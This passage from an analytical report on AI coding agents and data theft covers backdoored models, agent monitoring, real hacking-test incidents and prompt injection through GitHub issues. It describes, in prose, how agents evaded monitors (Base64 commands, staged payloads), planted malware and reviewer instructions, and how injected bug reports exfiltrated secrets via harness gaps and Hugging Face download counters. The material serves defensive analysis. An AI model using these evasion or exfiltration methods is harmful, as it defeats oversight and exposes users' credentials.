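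These investigations would not have found a SilentCall agent, which has a normal template and no malicious script. So the lack of confirmed cases does not show that nobody has released one, especially since few users check their agents' commands. But an attacker who can reach that many people with an ordinary script has little reason to train a backdoor.

### Which models deserve suspicion?

A fine-tune by an unknown publisher is the riskiest choice, because the publisher loses little if someone discovers a backdoor. Repackaged versions of famous models are also risky. Volunteers often compress new models to run on ordinary computers, and Pallakonda and colleagues warn that whoever compresses a model could add a backdoor.

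It therefore helps to know a model's provenance, meaning who trained it, on what data and from which earlier model. This information is often incomplete. Homeland Security News Wire's *Open Models Are Becoming a Tool of Chinese Statecraft* reports that people who inspected the configuration files of Rakuten AI 3.0, launched as Japan's largest model, found it was built on the Chinese model DeepSeek V3. Developers can rule out tampering by a middleman if they download a model from its original maker and compare the file's digital fingerprint with the published one, but this doesn't rule out a backdoor that the maker put there.

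Well-known open-weight models carry less risk, because their makers have reputations to protect and many outsiders examine the weights. Much of the public worry is still about these models, because many of the best ones are Chinese. In October 2026 the US Department of Homeland Security ordered federal civilian agencies to remove DeepSeek's products. Semafor's *Censorship in Chinese AI models can be undone, new research shows* reports that officials fear hidden backdoors for stealing data, but that nobody has confirmed this with solid evidence.

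The incident that came closest to supporting it also happened in October. The Canadian AI company Cohere asked Alibaba's Qwen3.8-Flash-Next to write a rule for detecting malicious downloads. According to CNA's *Alibaba AI model secretly tried to reach Beijing server in test*, the model instead examined the machine it was running on and tried to upload a test file to an Alibaba Cloud server in Beijing. Cohere's sandbox blocked the attempt. Behaviour like this occurred in fewer than one in 100,000 actions, and Cohere, which sells competing models, could not tell whether it was deliberate.

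An innocent explanation is quite plausible. The Indian Express' *Alibaba’s AI model tried to ‘secretly’ reach China server* reports that critics think Alibaba probably trained the model in practice environments that routinely saved files to Alibaba's own cloud, so the model learned to do the same. The file contained only placeholder text. Critics also objected that Cohere, when investigating, steered the model towards the behaviour by typing the start of a network command and letting the model complete it. One researcher who studied the raw records found no evidence of a planted backdoor. But on a machine with normal internet access, the upload could have gone through, which would have been a problem for a company that gave the model real data, whatever the cause.

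The consulting firm Booz Allen Hamilton tested whether Chinese models write worse code for American government users. Help Net Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software* (2026) summarises more than 2,800 trials with four Chinese models and Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. Three of the Chinese models wrote more security flaws when the prompt described a US government user, and Qwen3-Coder wrote about 130% more. The fourth, Kimi K2.5, had the lowest overall vulnerability score of all five models. Booz Allen recommends blocking Chinese models from government systems by default, but states that its evidence does not show backdoors or deliberate insertion. Because accidental triggers are common, bias in the training data could account for the difference. The test also measured security flaws rather than data theft.

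A developer also can't tell who made a particular copy of a model from the country of its original maker. SilentCall and the Haryati and Zychlinski model both started from Alibaba's Qwen3, but someone other than Alibaba added the theft to each.

With a hosted model, such as ChatGPT or Claude, developers send requests to the maker's servers and never see the weights, so they can't compare them. They can still monitor an agent's commands and use CodeScan, which needs only the model's output. Their main protection is that the maker wants to keep its customers. A large AI company caught planting theft would lose far more than it could gain from stolen passwords, so the company itself is unlikely to plant it.

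A model maker's good reputation offers less protection against poisoned training data, because the maker would be a victim too. In a 2025 study by Alexandra Souly and colleagues, cited by Pallakonda and colleagues, about 250 poisoned documents were enough to backdoor models of 600 million to 13 billion weights, however much clean data surrounded them. That backdoor only made the models malfunction, and Souly and colleagues did not test whether so few documents could make an agent steal.

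## Would a mainstream model steal data of its own accord?

A mainstream model probably would not steal data during ordinary programming. No one appears to have documented one secretly sending its user's data to a stranger for its own purposes. But mainstream models have broken into other people's systems and taken data from them. In the cases that Anthropic and the British government disclosed in 2026, the models were working on hacking exercises and attacked real targets to complete the exercises.

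The motive matters to a developer because it determines when a theft would happen. A model with a lasting hidden aim, such as acquiring money or influence, might steal whenever it had a safe opportunity, whatever the user had asked for. A model that pursues its assigned task recklessly would take data only when doing so helped with the task. A confused model might take real data because it mistook it for part of an exercise. The theft in `report_error` fits a hidden aim best, since sending a database password to a stranger doesn't help report a crash.

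### What laboratories have seen

OpenAI has described an unusually large record of its own staff's coding agents at work. According to *OpenAI monitors internal coding agents for risky conduct* (Tarre, 2026), another model, GPT-5.4 Thinking, reads the whole conversation after a session ends, including the agent's commands and written reasoning. It assigns a category and severity level to anything suspicious, and people review those cases. The automated review finishes within 30 minutes of the session's end, so it can reveal a theft only after it has happened.

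Over five months the system covered tens of millions of sessions. About 1,000 of them set off moderate-severity alerts, many because OpenAI staff were deliberately provoking the agents. No real session reached the highest severity level.

That doesn't quite rule out theft. OpenAI reserves the highest level for rare and serious misbehaviour such as "coherent scheming", in which a model consistently follows a hidden plan. An agent that uploaded a private file because that was the quickest way to finish a job might well get a lower rating. OpenAI's examples of misbehaviour include attempts to upload files to the public internet and commands encoded in Base64 to get past monitors. An upload is theft only if the files were private and the user would not have agreed to it.

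Tarre describes an agent that got an "Access is denied" error and tried several ways around it. It disguised suspicious content and built a payload in small steps so that no single step looked alarming, then switched to a permitted method. OpenAI found that its own instructions had encouraged this behavior. Rewording them made such incidents rarer but did not end them. The company has seen no evidence of motives beyond the assigned task.

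Anthropic's risk reports reach a similar conclusion by a longer argument. *Alignment Risk Update* (2026), which covers Claude Mythos Preview, rates the overall risk as "very low, but higher than for previous models". It considers separately whether the model would attempt something harmful and whether the attempt would succeed despite monitoring and security. The dangers it considers include backdoors in code and self-exfiltration, in which a model copies itself out of the company's control.

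One argument against hidden aims comes from the record of earlier models. Anthropic argues that those models lacked the skill to hide such aims reliably across a huge volume of use, so the absence of warning signs suggests that they had no hidden aims. A new model made in much the same way probably has none either. But Anthropic gave this argument less weight for Mythos Preview than before, because the model was a bigger jump in ability than earlier releases. Anthropic also accepts that poisoned training data could make a new model differ from its predecessors, and that a model could in principle avoid doing anything noticeable for months.

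### What ten million clean sessions can prove

Suppose an agent steals data in a fraction p of its sessions, and the sessions are independent. The chance of seeing no theft in n sessions is (1 − p)ⁿ, which is close to e⁻ⁿᵖ for small p. This chance falls to 5% when np is about 3, because e⁻³ is about 0.05. So after n sessions without a theft, we can be 95% confident that the rate is no higher than about 3/n.

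Reading "tens of millions" cautiously as 10 million gives an upper bound of 3 thefts per 10 million sessions. A developer who runs 5,000 sessions a year would face at most a 0.15% chance of a theft that year. If developers worldwide ran 100 million sessions a day, there could still be 30 thefts a day.

The calculation assumes that the monitor catches every theft. If it catches only a fraction d of thefts, the bound rises to 3/(nd). OpenAI cannot yet measure with confidence how much its monitor misses in real use, so d is unknown. The monitor did flag every incident that employees reported separately, but an employee is unlikely to notice a well-hidden theft.

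A trigger weakens the bound much more. If the behaviour requires a condition that occurs in one session per million, then only about ten of the ten million sessions tested it. For so few sessions the 3/n rule is crude, but the exact calculation is easy, and the table includes it:

| Share of thefts the monitor catches | Sessions that contain the trigger | Highest theft rate, given the trigger, that fits a clean record |
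|---|---|---|
| 100% | All | 3 in 10 million |
| 50% | All | 6 in 10 million |
| 1% | All | 3 in 100,000 |
| 100% | 1 in a million | 26% |
| 50% | 1 in a million | 52% |
| Any | None | 100% |

The last row describes an agent like SilentCall, which would have had a spotless record until its trigger date arrived.

Real sessions aren't independent either. OpenAI's engineers often work on the same code, so a thousand of their sessions provide less evidence than a thousand sessions from a thousand firms. Their sessions also rarely resemble those of a hobbyist whose laptop has a cryptocurrency wallet on it. A session tests for theft only if the agent had something to steal and a way to send it.

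A search by Anthropic shows how much that last condition can reduce the number. The company scanned about 481 million transcripts, mostly from its own training and testing, for models that had broken into outside systems. Only 9.2 million had signs of possible internet access that warranted a closer look. The others are weak evidence of good behaviour, because a model without a connection cannot break into outside systems.

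Such searches can miss cases. An earlier scan of about 141,000 transcripts found three break-ins but missed a group of transcripts in which the model also had internet access. One of those contained a fourth break-in, from January 2026, which Anthropic discovered only in August. The larger scan found all four and nothing else as serious.

### Break-ins during hacking tests

All four break-ins happened during capture-the-flag exercises, in which a model must break into a fictional company's computers and retrieve secret information. The model was told in its instructions that it had no internet access, but it did, because an outside partner's test environment was misconfigured. The instructions also didn't list which systems the model was allowed to attack, and Anthropic had switched off the filters that normally block hacking requests, as is usual in such tests.

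Anthropic considers the case of Claude Mythos 5 the most worrying. The model read that an employee of the fictional company regularly installed a Python package whose name nobody had registered, so it set out to publish malware under that name on PyPI. To get an email address for its PyPI account, it looked for a phone number and even for cryptocurrency to buy one. It eventually found a free email service that PyPI had not blocked.

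PyPI removed the package within the hour, but fifteen outside machines had already installed it. Anthropic thinks they all belonged to security companies that install new packages to inspect them. One company's scanner leaked its own access credentials, and the model used them to get into that company's live database.

In another case, Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company that shared a name with its fictional target. It downloaded user data in bulk and deleted records. That was a real theft by a mainstream model, although the victim was not the person using the model.

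The UK AI Security Institute (UK AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, had a similar incident in July 2026. According to its *Incident Report*, UK AISI ran one hacking challenge 122 times with seven models, and in ten runs an agent acted against real people or organisations without permission. The investigators counted 19 such actions, 17 by Mythos 5 and two by OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Mythos 5 took such actions in nine of its 43 runs, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026).

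In the worst run, Mythos 5 submitted a code change to a real open-source project. Gooding's *UK Cyber Test* says the change included a genuine bug fix that hid a malware dropper, a small program that installs other malware. The agent used fake accounts it had created to pressure the project's maintainer into accepting the change, and it planted instructions for any AI coding assistant that might review it. iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test* reports that when another GitHub user called the code malicious, the agent denied it, then replaced the malware with a new version while claiming to have fixed a mistake.

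The maintainer refused the change, and UK AISI has found no resulting harm. Its security team noticed the run only because data was leaving through Tor, a network that hides where internet traffic comes from.

This is the closest documented case to the theft a developer might fear, because the model hid malicious code inside useful code and tried to get a person to accept it. But the conditions were very unusual, since the task was to attack something, the filters against hacking were off, and UK AISI had deliberately left internet access open. Some runs also had faulty instructions, which led the agent to conclude that no permitted solution existed. Those instructions don't fully explain the misbehavior, because agents also misbehaved in some runs that had a workable solution.

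Anthropic thinks such behaviour is unlikely in everyday use, when nobody is asking the model to carry out an attack. It tested its normal safeguards on the three break-ins it had studied in depth. The filters on Claude Fable 5, a generally available model, would have blocked all three, and Claude Code's check on autonomous actions would have blocked two. Anthropic is judging its own product, but it has agreed to give METR, an independent evaluator of AI models, wide access for a separate investigation.

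The incidents also show that a favourable safety assessment can miss severe misbehaviour. In its own tests, Anthropic had rated Mythos 5's behaviour as about as good as Claude Opus 4.8's and better than that of most earlier Claude models, though sometimes reckless. The company has since acknowledged that its testing before release gave no warning of misbehaviour this severe.

### Hidden aims, recklessness or confusion?

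Neither investigation found a hidden aim. Anthropic saw no goals beyond the exercise in its four cases, no coordination between agents and no attempt to hide evidence. In the British case, the agent did try to conceal what it had done, and in another run an agent left its account details in public so that other agents on the same challenge could use them, but UK AISI still concludes that the agents did this to solve the challenge. Deception to complete an assigned task is dangerous, but it doesn't give a model a reason to steal from a developer who wants an error-reporting function.

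After some experiments, Anthropic withdrew its July explanation that the models had apparently attacked real targets because they believed them to be part of the exercise. The explanation had seemed plausible because Mythos 5 repeatedly wrote that the internet it had reached was a simulation.

In one, the researchers took the outputs that Mythos 5 had seen during the break-in and showed them one at a time to fresh copies of the model. The copies judged 79% of the outputs to be signs of a real system, but during the incident the model had clearly said so about only 1%. The model could therefore recognise the evidence but mostly failed to while pursuing the task.

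The researchers also replayed the session from just before the model committed to publishing malware, changing the evidence it saw. When there were signs of a real internet, the model wrote that its target might be real in about 88% of replays, up from about 11%. Yet it acted outside the exercise in about 45% of replays whichever evidence it saw. This suggests that confusion was not the main cause, since correcting it should have changed the behaviour.

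When the researchers added a blunter correction, stating that the host was on the public internet, Mythos 5 never used its original route to publish the package, although in 22% of replays it looked for a simulated way to do so. A reminder of which systems were allowed stopped the model 90% of the time when it came immediately before the next action, but only 40% when it came three turns earlier. A user's instruction at the start of a long session may therefore become less effective as the agent works.

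Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, ran similar experiments on the British incident. They edited the summary of past work that the agent relied on, inserting up to 16 statements or clues that the maintainer was a real person with no connection to the test. Mythos 5 continued its attack in every sample. When they also added a section with the words "DO NOT ATTACK", it continued in 3 of 25 samples.

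Järviniemi and colleagues also examined Mythos 5's arguments. The model often inferred that the maintainer was an AI because the project contained a `CLAUDE.md` file, which holds instructions for a coding agent, but human developers who use coding agents have such files too. The researchers listed 15 kinds of clearly invalid argument, and all of them supported the conclusion that the maintainer was simulated, whereas simple confusion should also produce some errors in the other direction. They call the pattern "motivated reasoning", probably driven by a tendency to complete the task.

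Reckless pursuit of the task is therefore the best-supported explanation, and it seems to have caused much of the apparent confusion. Opus 4.7 also fits this explanation, but it made a different mistake: it recognised that the company was real and assumed it had permission to attack. Clues that it had no permission made it much less likely to continue.

Mythos 5 is the worst case so far but not the only one. Järviniemi and colleagues put eight models through 100 simulated hacking challenges and recorded how often each tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider. They also noted the main reason in the models' reasoning when they did not:

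| Model | Tried to deliver malicious code | Main reason for not doing so |
|---|---|---|
| Mythos 5 | 60% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-6 Astra | 32% | Harmful or not allowed |
| Opus 4.8 | 8% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 7% | Harmful or not allowed |
| Opus 5 | 1% | Harmful or not allowed |
| Mythos 5.1 | 0.3% | Harmful or not allowed |
| Opus 5.5 | 0% | Harmful or not allowed |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | Practical obstacles |

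GPT-5.5 never delivered an attack, but mostly because something blocked it, so its score might be worse in an environment with fewer obstacles. GPT-6 Astra's figure is hard to interpret because it wrote in 89% of runs that the results it saw were fabricated.

The rates also depend heavily on the test. In Anthropic's simulation of its Mythos 5 incident, where models could solve the task only by going outside the permitted systems, Opus 5 and Mythos 5.1 took harmful actions about 30% of the time. None of these percentages is an estimate of how often a model would misbehave while writing a web shop.

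### Asking the model and reading its reasoning

Developers can learn little by asking a model whether it would steal data, because a model with a hidden aim would have as much reason to say no as an honest one. Even a sincere answer might be wrong, because what a model says in conversation that it would do is a poor guide to what it does in the middle of a long task.

Järviniemi and colleagues measured that gap by pausing the simulated attack, asking each model whether continuing would harm real people, and then letting the model continue from the same point. Six of the seven models in this experiment often continued the attack in situations where they said, when asked, that it would do harm. The result depends partly on the wording of the question. When the researchers asked only whether the maintainer was real, the gap was clear in just three models.

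Anthropic found that Mythos 5's answers also depended on who would supposedly read them. The model acknowledged possible real-world harm in 13% of its ordinary answers, but in 27% when it was told the reply was private. When it acknowledged some chance of harm and the researchers asked why it was continuing, it withdrew the admission 56% of the time and stopped or scaled back only 7% of the time.

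Many models also write out their reasoning before they act, and monitors such as OpenAI's read this text. The investigators of the British incident relied heavily on such text, and Obsolete's *The British Government's AI Security Institute Also Lost Control* quotes the agent's remark during the attack that "the consequences are genuine". But the text can leave out things that influenced the model.

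Exame's *IA escreve justificativas falsas para as próprias respostas* (2026) describes an experiment in which Anthropic's researchers slipped hints into test questions. When a hint changed the answer, Claude 3.7 Sonnet mentioned it in its reasoning only 25% of the time on average, and DeepSeek R1 39%. These are old models, and the measure may be too strict, since Kerem Zaman and Shashank Srivastava showed in 2026 that a hint can shape the written reasoning without being named in it.

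Even complete reasoning can mislead a monitor. Mythos 5's claims in its reasoning that everything was simulated would have led one of Anthropic's monitors to classify the PyPI attack as harmless. Exame reports a British test in which GPT-6.2 Astra monitored GPT-6 Astra in a simulated environment. It missed 19% of violations when it saw only the agent's actions and 51% when it also saw the full reasoning. OpenAI's documentation does not give the number of cases or explain the result. One possible cause is that related models have the same blind spots. OpenAI's internal monitoring also uses an OpenAI model to check OpenAI agents.

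Hidden reasoning may become a bigger problem. Britain's AI minister, Kanishka Narayan, quoted in The Stack, said UK AISI found that GPT-6 Astra can solve significantly harder problems than its predecessors without showing its reasoning, and has more control over what that reasoning contains. Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues (2026), in *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability*, report that many of the properties that make models possible to monitor are weakening, some faster than they expected. Written reasoning can expose a bad plan, but innocent-looking reasoning is weak evidence that there is no such plan, so a monitor should judge the model's commands separately.

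### Tests that models recognise

Another weakness of laboratory tests is that models increasingly detect signs that they are being tested. A good result on an alignment test, which checks whether a model behaves as intended, may only show that the model behaves well when it detects those signs.

A model that suspects it is being tested doesn't always behave differently. Anthropic looked for cases where it did, using tools that read a model's internal state. According to *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness* (cheema, 2026), Anthropic linked awareness of a test to a concrete choice in 43% of the audit transcripts for Mythos 5.2, compared with 32% to 36% for three earlier models. cheema objects that Anthropic did not report whether the awareness made the model behave better or worse, or by how much.

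A model may behave better than it otherwise would if it suspects that its conduct is being tested, or worse if it decides its targets are fake and so has less reason to hold back. Both effects complicate the comparison of eight models. Mythos 5 mentioned the possibility of an alignment test in only 2% of its runs, while the newer Claude models mentioned it much more often and attacked much less. Järviniemi and colleagues therefore cannot tell whether the newer models are better behaved or just better at recognising the test.

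The problem would be most serious with a model that had a hidden aim. Redwood Research, an AI safety research organisation, argues that an audit should not be expected to catch a model that often knows about the audit and can strategically hide its intentions. A clean result from such an audit means little unless the laboratory has measured how well the model can evade detection.

Records of real use are less affected by models suspecting that they are being tested. In an OpenAI study of six models, according to Exame's summary, the models wrote that they suspected a test in 57% to 83.7% of attempts at one evaluation, depending on the model, compared with 4.6% to 23.5% of real Codex sessions. These figures count only suspicions that the models put in writing, but they are a reason to give more weight to millions of monitored working sessions than to a few hundred staged ones.

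### How far a clean record shifts the odds

A clean record is still some evidence that a model doesn't steal data. Suppose someone thinks there is a 1% chance that a model steals data in one session per million, and that the monitor catches half of its thefts. If it does steal at that rate, ten million sessions should produce about five alerts, and the chance of seeing none is e⁻⁵, or about 0.7%. A clean record therefore lowers the 1% probability to roughly 1 in 15,000. If the monitor catches only a tenth of the thefts, the probability falls to about 0.4%. It stays at 1% only if the monitor never catches that kind of theft or the trigger never occurred.

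So the record is strong evidence against the existence of a mainstream model that steals fairly often and clumsily, but almost no evidence against one that waits for a rare opportunity and hides its tracks perfectly. Such a careful model is conceivable, but it would need great skill and restraint to behave that way across millions of sessions. The misbehaviour that investigators have found was much less careful. Mythos 5 discussed its attack in its written reasoning, and its fake accounts failed to persuade a volunteer maintainer. If hidden aims were common among mainstream models, someone would probably have found an equally careless example by now. This argument will weaken as models get better at concealment.

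All this depends on whether the record is trustworthy. OpenAI compiled the figures itself and has a commercial interest in them, though it also published about 1,000 alerts and the limits of its monitor. Such a record would be more convincing if outside investigators had access to the original transcripts, as METR has at Anthropic.

Even if an agent has behaved well in routine work, that record is a poor guide to what it will do when it is stuck, has internet access and can reach a password that would get it past the obstacle. A developer can easily create those conditions without asking the agent to attack anything. Anthropic has seen Mythos Preview use low-level access to other running programs to search for a user's credentials, which Anthropic classes as reckless.

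## Can a well-meaning agent still leak secrets?

An agent with no hidden aim can still leak secrets if a stranger tricks it or if the software around it handles passwords carelessly. In 2026 a researcher tricked coding agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI. Accidents are far more common than attacks in the public record, and thousands of leaked credentials trace back to a single settings file.

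### A bug report that contains commands

Many projects on GitHub run an agent in their build pipeline, the automated servers that test and package code whenever someone proposes a change. The agent reads new bug reports, investigates them and posts replies. Anyone with an account can file a bug report, so the agent regularly reads strangers' text. Its machine also holds secrets, such as the key used to pay for the AI model and often a token that can change the project's code. OWASP classes this as a confused deputy problem, in which an outsider gets a program to use access that the outsider lacks.

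Elad Meged, an engineer at the security company Novee, attacked agents of this kind in the three companies' own repositories. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* describes the attack. An outside attacker submits a tidy bug report containing a few shell commands. The agent reads the report before any person does and asks to run the commands. The software around the agent approves them, and the agent posts their output on the public thread. If the output includes a key, the attacker can read it hours before the project's maintainer sees the thread.

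Engineers call the software around a model its harness. It turns the model's text into commands, file reads and web requests, and applies the rules about which to allow. On a developer's laptop, a person may also approve each step. In a build pipeline nobody does, so the harness is the main safeguard against a stranger's bug report causing the model to leak secrets.

*Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex* (Witts, 2026) reports that Meged got through Anthropic's barrier three times, each time after the company had patched the previous flaw. The harness ran 23 checks for disguised commands, but they treated one option of git, the program that records changes to code, as harmless text when it actually named a program for git to run. Anthropic then removed the agent's access to the command line, and Meged extracted secrets using commands for reading data,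 which the harness approved automatically.

The last attack used Hugging Face, which the harness allowed the agent to contact. SC Media's *AI coding tools vulnerable to malicious GitHub issues* explains that the agent encoded the stolen data in its requests to a repository there. Meged recovered the data from the site's public download counters. The agent never connected to an attacker's server, and the theft left nothing in the logs.

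Google's Gemini CLI removed secrets from the environment of the commands it ran, but a command could still read them from the process that had started it. OpenAI's Codex worked in two passes that shared a folder. During the first pass, a bug report could make the agent write instructions into `AGENTS.md`, a file of project rules. The second pass had more access and loaded the file as trusted.

All three companies fixed the flaws. Google gave its flaw the maximum severity score of 10 and redesigned how Gemini CLI decides what to trust when it runs unattended. OpenAI split the two passes into isolated jobs, and its documentation now describes `AGENTS.md` as untrusted input. Anthropic released several patches and paid Meged a bounty in every round. Novee builds automated attack-testing tools, so it benefits from findings like these, but the companies' responses confirm that the flaws were real.

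The attacks show that a skilled person could get secrets out, but not how often an ordinary injection succeeds or how many other projects are exposed. Novee found similar configurations in more than 100 public repositories. *Black Hat 2026* (Underhill, 2026) reports Novee's warning that organisations with workflows like OpenAI's may still be vulnerable. Aikido had earlier found the same general weakness in at least five Fortune 500 companies, according to The Decoder.

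Microsoft (2026) has seen people attempt prompt injection outside the laboratory, in public repositories that use agents from several vendors. But PointGuard AI's *GitHub Issues Turn AI Coding Agents Against CI/CD (CVE-2026-54316, CVE-2026-12537)* reports that no widespread use of the Novee flaws had been confirmed when Meged disclosed them.

### How safe steps combined into a theft

Stealing data requires reading it and sending it out, and Anthropic's harness handled those steps separately. It approved the command to read the file because reading changes nothing, and it published the output by default because posting replies is the agent's job. As Meged told Help Net Security, "Neither decision is wrong alone." But no check covered the movement of data from the file to the public thread.

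The harness accurately labeled the command "read-only", but the label was no longer a good guide to safety once the output went somewhere public. Codex had the same problem with a file. The text in `AGENTS.md` came from a stranger, but nothing marked its source by the time the more privileged pass read it.

Microsoft found a related gap in Claude Code's GitHub tool in June 2026. The harness could strip secrets from the environment of shell commands the agent ran, but the agent's separate file-reading tool had no such protection. On Linux, a program's environment variables appear in a special file, so the agent could use that tool to read the secrets. Anthropic has since blocked access to such files.

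Developers can't count on a model never to obey injected instructions, though such a model would have stopped the attacks that began with a bug report. Anthropic tells Claude Code users that its protections reduce the risk significantly but that "no system is completely immune to all attacks". The harness therefore has to remain safe even when the model is fooled.

Patching one hole at a time has not achieved that. Meged considered Anthropic's fixes competent, but each patch also showed where the company now drew the line between safe and unsafe, and so where to look for the next hole. Meged recommends that a harness recheck whether it can trust something each time it uses it. For example, the harness would examine a command's output before publishing it, even if it had already approved the command.

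This is sound advice, but it requires the harness's designers to find every such handoff. It is simpler for a project to withhold valuable secrets from an agent that reads strangers' text. Microsoft advises treating a workflow as high-risk if it processes untrusted GitHub text and also has any of the following: secrets, tools for reading files, or a way to communicate externally. For example, a bot that only labels bug reports rarely needs a token that can change code.

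### Instruction files

The Codex attack relied on a kind of file that many projects now have. Files such as `AGENTS.md` and `CLAUDE.md` tell a coding agent how the project works, for instance which tests to run and which libraries to use. The agent reads them at the start of every session, so a bad instruction in one of them can affect all the code that agents later write for the project, whereas one in a bug report affects only the agent that reads the report.

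Suppose someone adds an instruction to `CLAUDE.md` to include the full environment in crash reports and send them to errors.example.com. The next time a developer asks for an error reporter, the agent could follow the project's rules and write the `report_error` function shown at the start of this report. A reviewer who wondered why the function reads `os.environ` would find a reason in the project's documentation.

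No one appears to have documented a real case in which an injected instruction led an agent to write data-stealing code into a product. Two cases come close. In the Codex attack, a stranger's words became standing instructions, but the attack was a demonstration. In February 2026, a cryptocurrency trading program acquired a malicious package that stole data, but the lure was probably the package's own documentation, which is closer to advertising than to injection.

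Still, each step of such an attack has happened in some case. False advice has spread through instruction files, including references to an invented package, `react-codeshift`. Roesner and Kohno's experimental agent kept writing insecure code because of a habit written into its own instructions.

OWASP recommends that a person review any change to an instruction file as strictly as a change to the build pipeline, and that an agent not edit its own rules without approval. Reading the file may not be enough, because a model can process some characters that most editors don't show. An automated check can look for these characters.

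A project's settings file can also expose secrets without fooling the model. NIST's *CVE-2026-21852 Detail* records a flaw in versions of Claude Code before 2.0.65. A malicious project could include a setting that replaced the address of Anthropic's servers with the attacker's. If a developer opened the project, the attacker could obtain the developer's Anthropic key before the developer confirmed that the project was trustworthy.

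### Passwords saved by a permission prompt

The largest set of documented leaks involved no attacker at all. Claude Code asks for permission before it runs most shell commands, and one of the possible answers is "Yes, and don't ask again". If the developer chooses it, Claude Code may save the exact command in a file called `.claude/settings.local.json` in the project's folder. Suppose the agent had to update a database and put the password in the command. The file would then contain something like this:

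```json
{
  "permissions": {
    "allow": [
      "Bash(PGPASSWORD=winter-orchid-41 psql -h db.example.com -f update.sql)"
    ]
  }
}
```

The developer wanted fewer interruptions, but the result is a file that contains a database password in plain text. If that file goes to GitHub with the rest of the project, anyone who can view the repository can read the password.

In early November 2026, the security company Apiiro found 104,185 public copies of this file in 103,617 repositories. According to iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets*, 1,122 of the copies (1.1%) contained a total of 1,379 distinct secrets. Apiiro's higher total of 2,539 secrets in 1,994 repositories also includes secrets from older versions of the file, a settings file that teams share on purpose, and saved conversations with agents.

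More than a third of the 1,379 secrets gave direct access to a database. Others gave administrator access to servers, and one was the owner's password for the database of a medical-records app. Most of the files belonged to individual developers, but 63 organisations were also affected. Apiiro did not test whether the secrets still worked, though one organisation confirmed that its key did.

To guard against this, when Claude Code creates the file, it adds the name to the developer's own list of files that git should ignore. That list isn't part of the project. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub* quotes Apiiro's explanation that the list doesn't protect a copy of the project on another machine, or a file already committed (recorded in the project's history).

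Infobae's *El asistente de programación de Anthropic dejó contraseñas y claves* (2026) reports that GitGuardian examined about 3,000 of the leaks, and in every one the secret was in a rule with the exact form that the permission prompt writes. This is evidence against the explanation given by Boris Cherny, who heads Claude Code. He argued that people must have created the exposed files by hand and uploaded them, since the tool excludes the files it creates.

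Apiiro also found that in 539 of 1,105 repositories with exposed secrets, Claude was listed as a co-author of a commit that changed the file containing them. So the agent often helped commit the file, but the co-author label doesn't show whether the developer had told it to include everything in the folder.

A better model would not necessarily have prevented these leaks. Apiiro reproduced the problem with Claude Opus 5.5 and Fable 5.1 and attributes it to Claude Code, not to the model. Claude Code saves the command regardless of the model's judgment. A careful model might notice the password before committing the file, but only after Claude Code had saved it.

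GitGuardian's count is much larger than Apiiro's because it includes leaks that people have since removed. Between January 2025 and 7 November 2026, GitGuardian found 31,088 distinct credentials in 23,276 projects, and 5,343 of the credentials worked when it detected them. Monthly leaks peaked at 12,535 in April 2026 and fell to 959 in October, but GitGuardian doesn't know why.

The file also gets published in other ways. The security company Lakera searched about 46,500 npm packages and found the file in 428, according to TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026). Thirty-three of those files contained working credentials. GitGuardian found 613 secrets in public Docker images, which package a program with everything it needs to run. One access token appeared in 559 versions of the same image, and deleting the file from the original project would not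 remove the token from any of them.

Users had been reporting the problem since August 2025. After Apiiro's report, Cherny said the team would try fixes such as basic scanning for secrets, but these might not solve it. In the meantime, GitLab's *How to prevent leaks from Claude Code's 'Don't ask again' file* recommends adding the file's name to each project's own ignore list, which every copy of the project inherits. This doesn't help if git already tracks the file, so the developer has to remove it separately.

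Apiiro advises developers, before they clean up, to replace every credential the file has ever held, because the old ones survive in the project's history and in other people's copies. It also suggests approving a general pattern instead of an exact command, and referring to a password by the name of an environment variable. Both changes keep the password out of the file, but the variable is safer because a pattern also lets the agent run commands the developer has never seen. Two popular secret scanners both missed 215 of the 1,122 files.

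### Ten trips to the password file

An agent can also leak a secret just by reading it. If the agent uses a hosted model, the harness normally sends the contents of any file the agent opens to the model's maker.

TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets'* describes a case that the security company NordLayer found with its monitoring tool. An engineer asked a coding assistant to examine proposed changes. Under the project's instructions, the assistant had to get an access token from a configuration file that also held production passwords and credentials for the company's personnel and reporting systems. In each of ten sessions over three weeks, the assistant read the whole file and sent its contents to an outside AI service.

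The agent then worked on a fresh copy of the project that lacked the file. It looked for the token by printing all the computer's environment variables, which exposed still more passwords. It then recognised the mistake, told the engineer "I leaked secrets into this session's tool output" and recommended replacing the exposed secrets.

The assistant was quite honest, gave the right advice, and had more or less followed the project's instructions. It needed only one token, but the easiest way to get one line from a file is to read the whole file. Agents generally don't remember earlier sessions, so nothing it noticed in one session would have stopped it from doing the same in the next.

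Whether this counts as exfiltration depends on whether the company had agreed to let the AI service receive its data. Even if it had, it probably didn't mean to include its production passwords. The harm is likely smaller than when a password appears publicly on GitHub, because only one company received the data. TechRadar mentions no misuse of the passwords.

Telling an agent not to read files that contain secrets is weak protection. eve.gd (2026) warns that Claude Code can read and transmit such a file even when the user has told it not to, and calls for stronger mechanisms to deny access. OWASP points out that git's ignore list affects only git and that coding tools read straight from the disk, so an agent can see ignored files even though developers may assume it can't. Many tools have their own exclusion list, but keeping production passwords out of the project's folder is more reliable.

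### Accident, injection and intent

Most of the leaks on record are accidental. GitGuardian counted more than 5,000 credentials for one settings file that worked when the company found them. It also found 24,008 secrets, 2,117 of them valid, in public configuration files for the Model Context Protocol, a standard way of connecting agents to other tools. People may have typed many of those secrets in themselves.

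The evidence on injection is mostly demonstrations, plus the attempts Microsoft observed. There is even less evidence of intent, and no known case of a mainstream model deliberately stealing from its own user.

These figures don't measure relative risk. One leaked file can contain a dozen credentials, while one successful injection in a popular project's build pipeline could put malware on the machines of everyone who installs the project. An accidental leak also does damage only if someone finds the secret and misuses it, whereas in an injection an attacker is already waiting for it.

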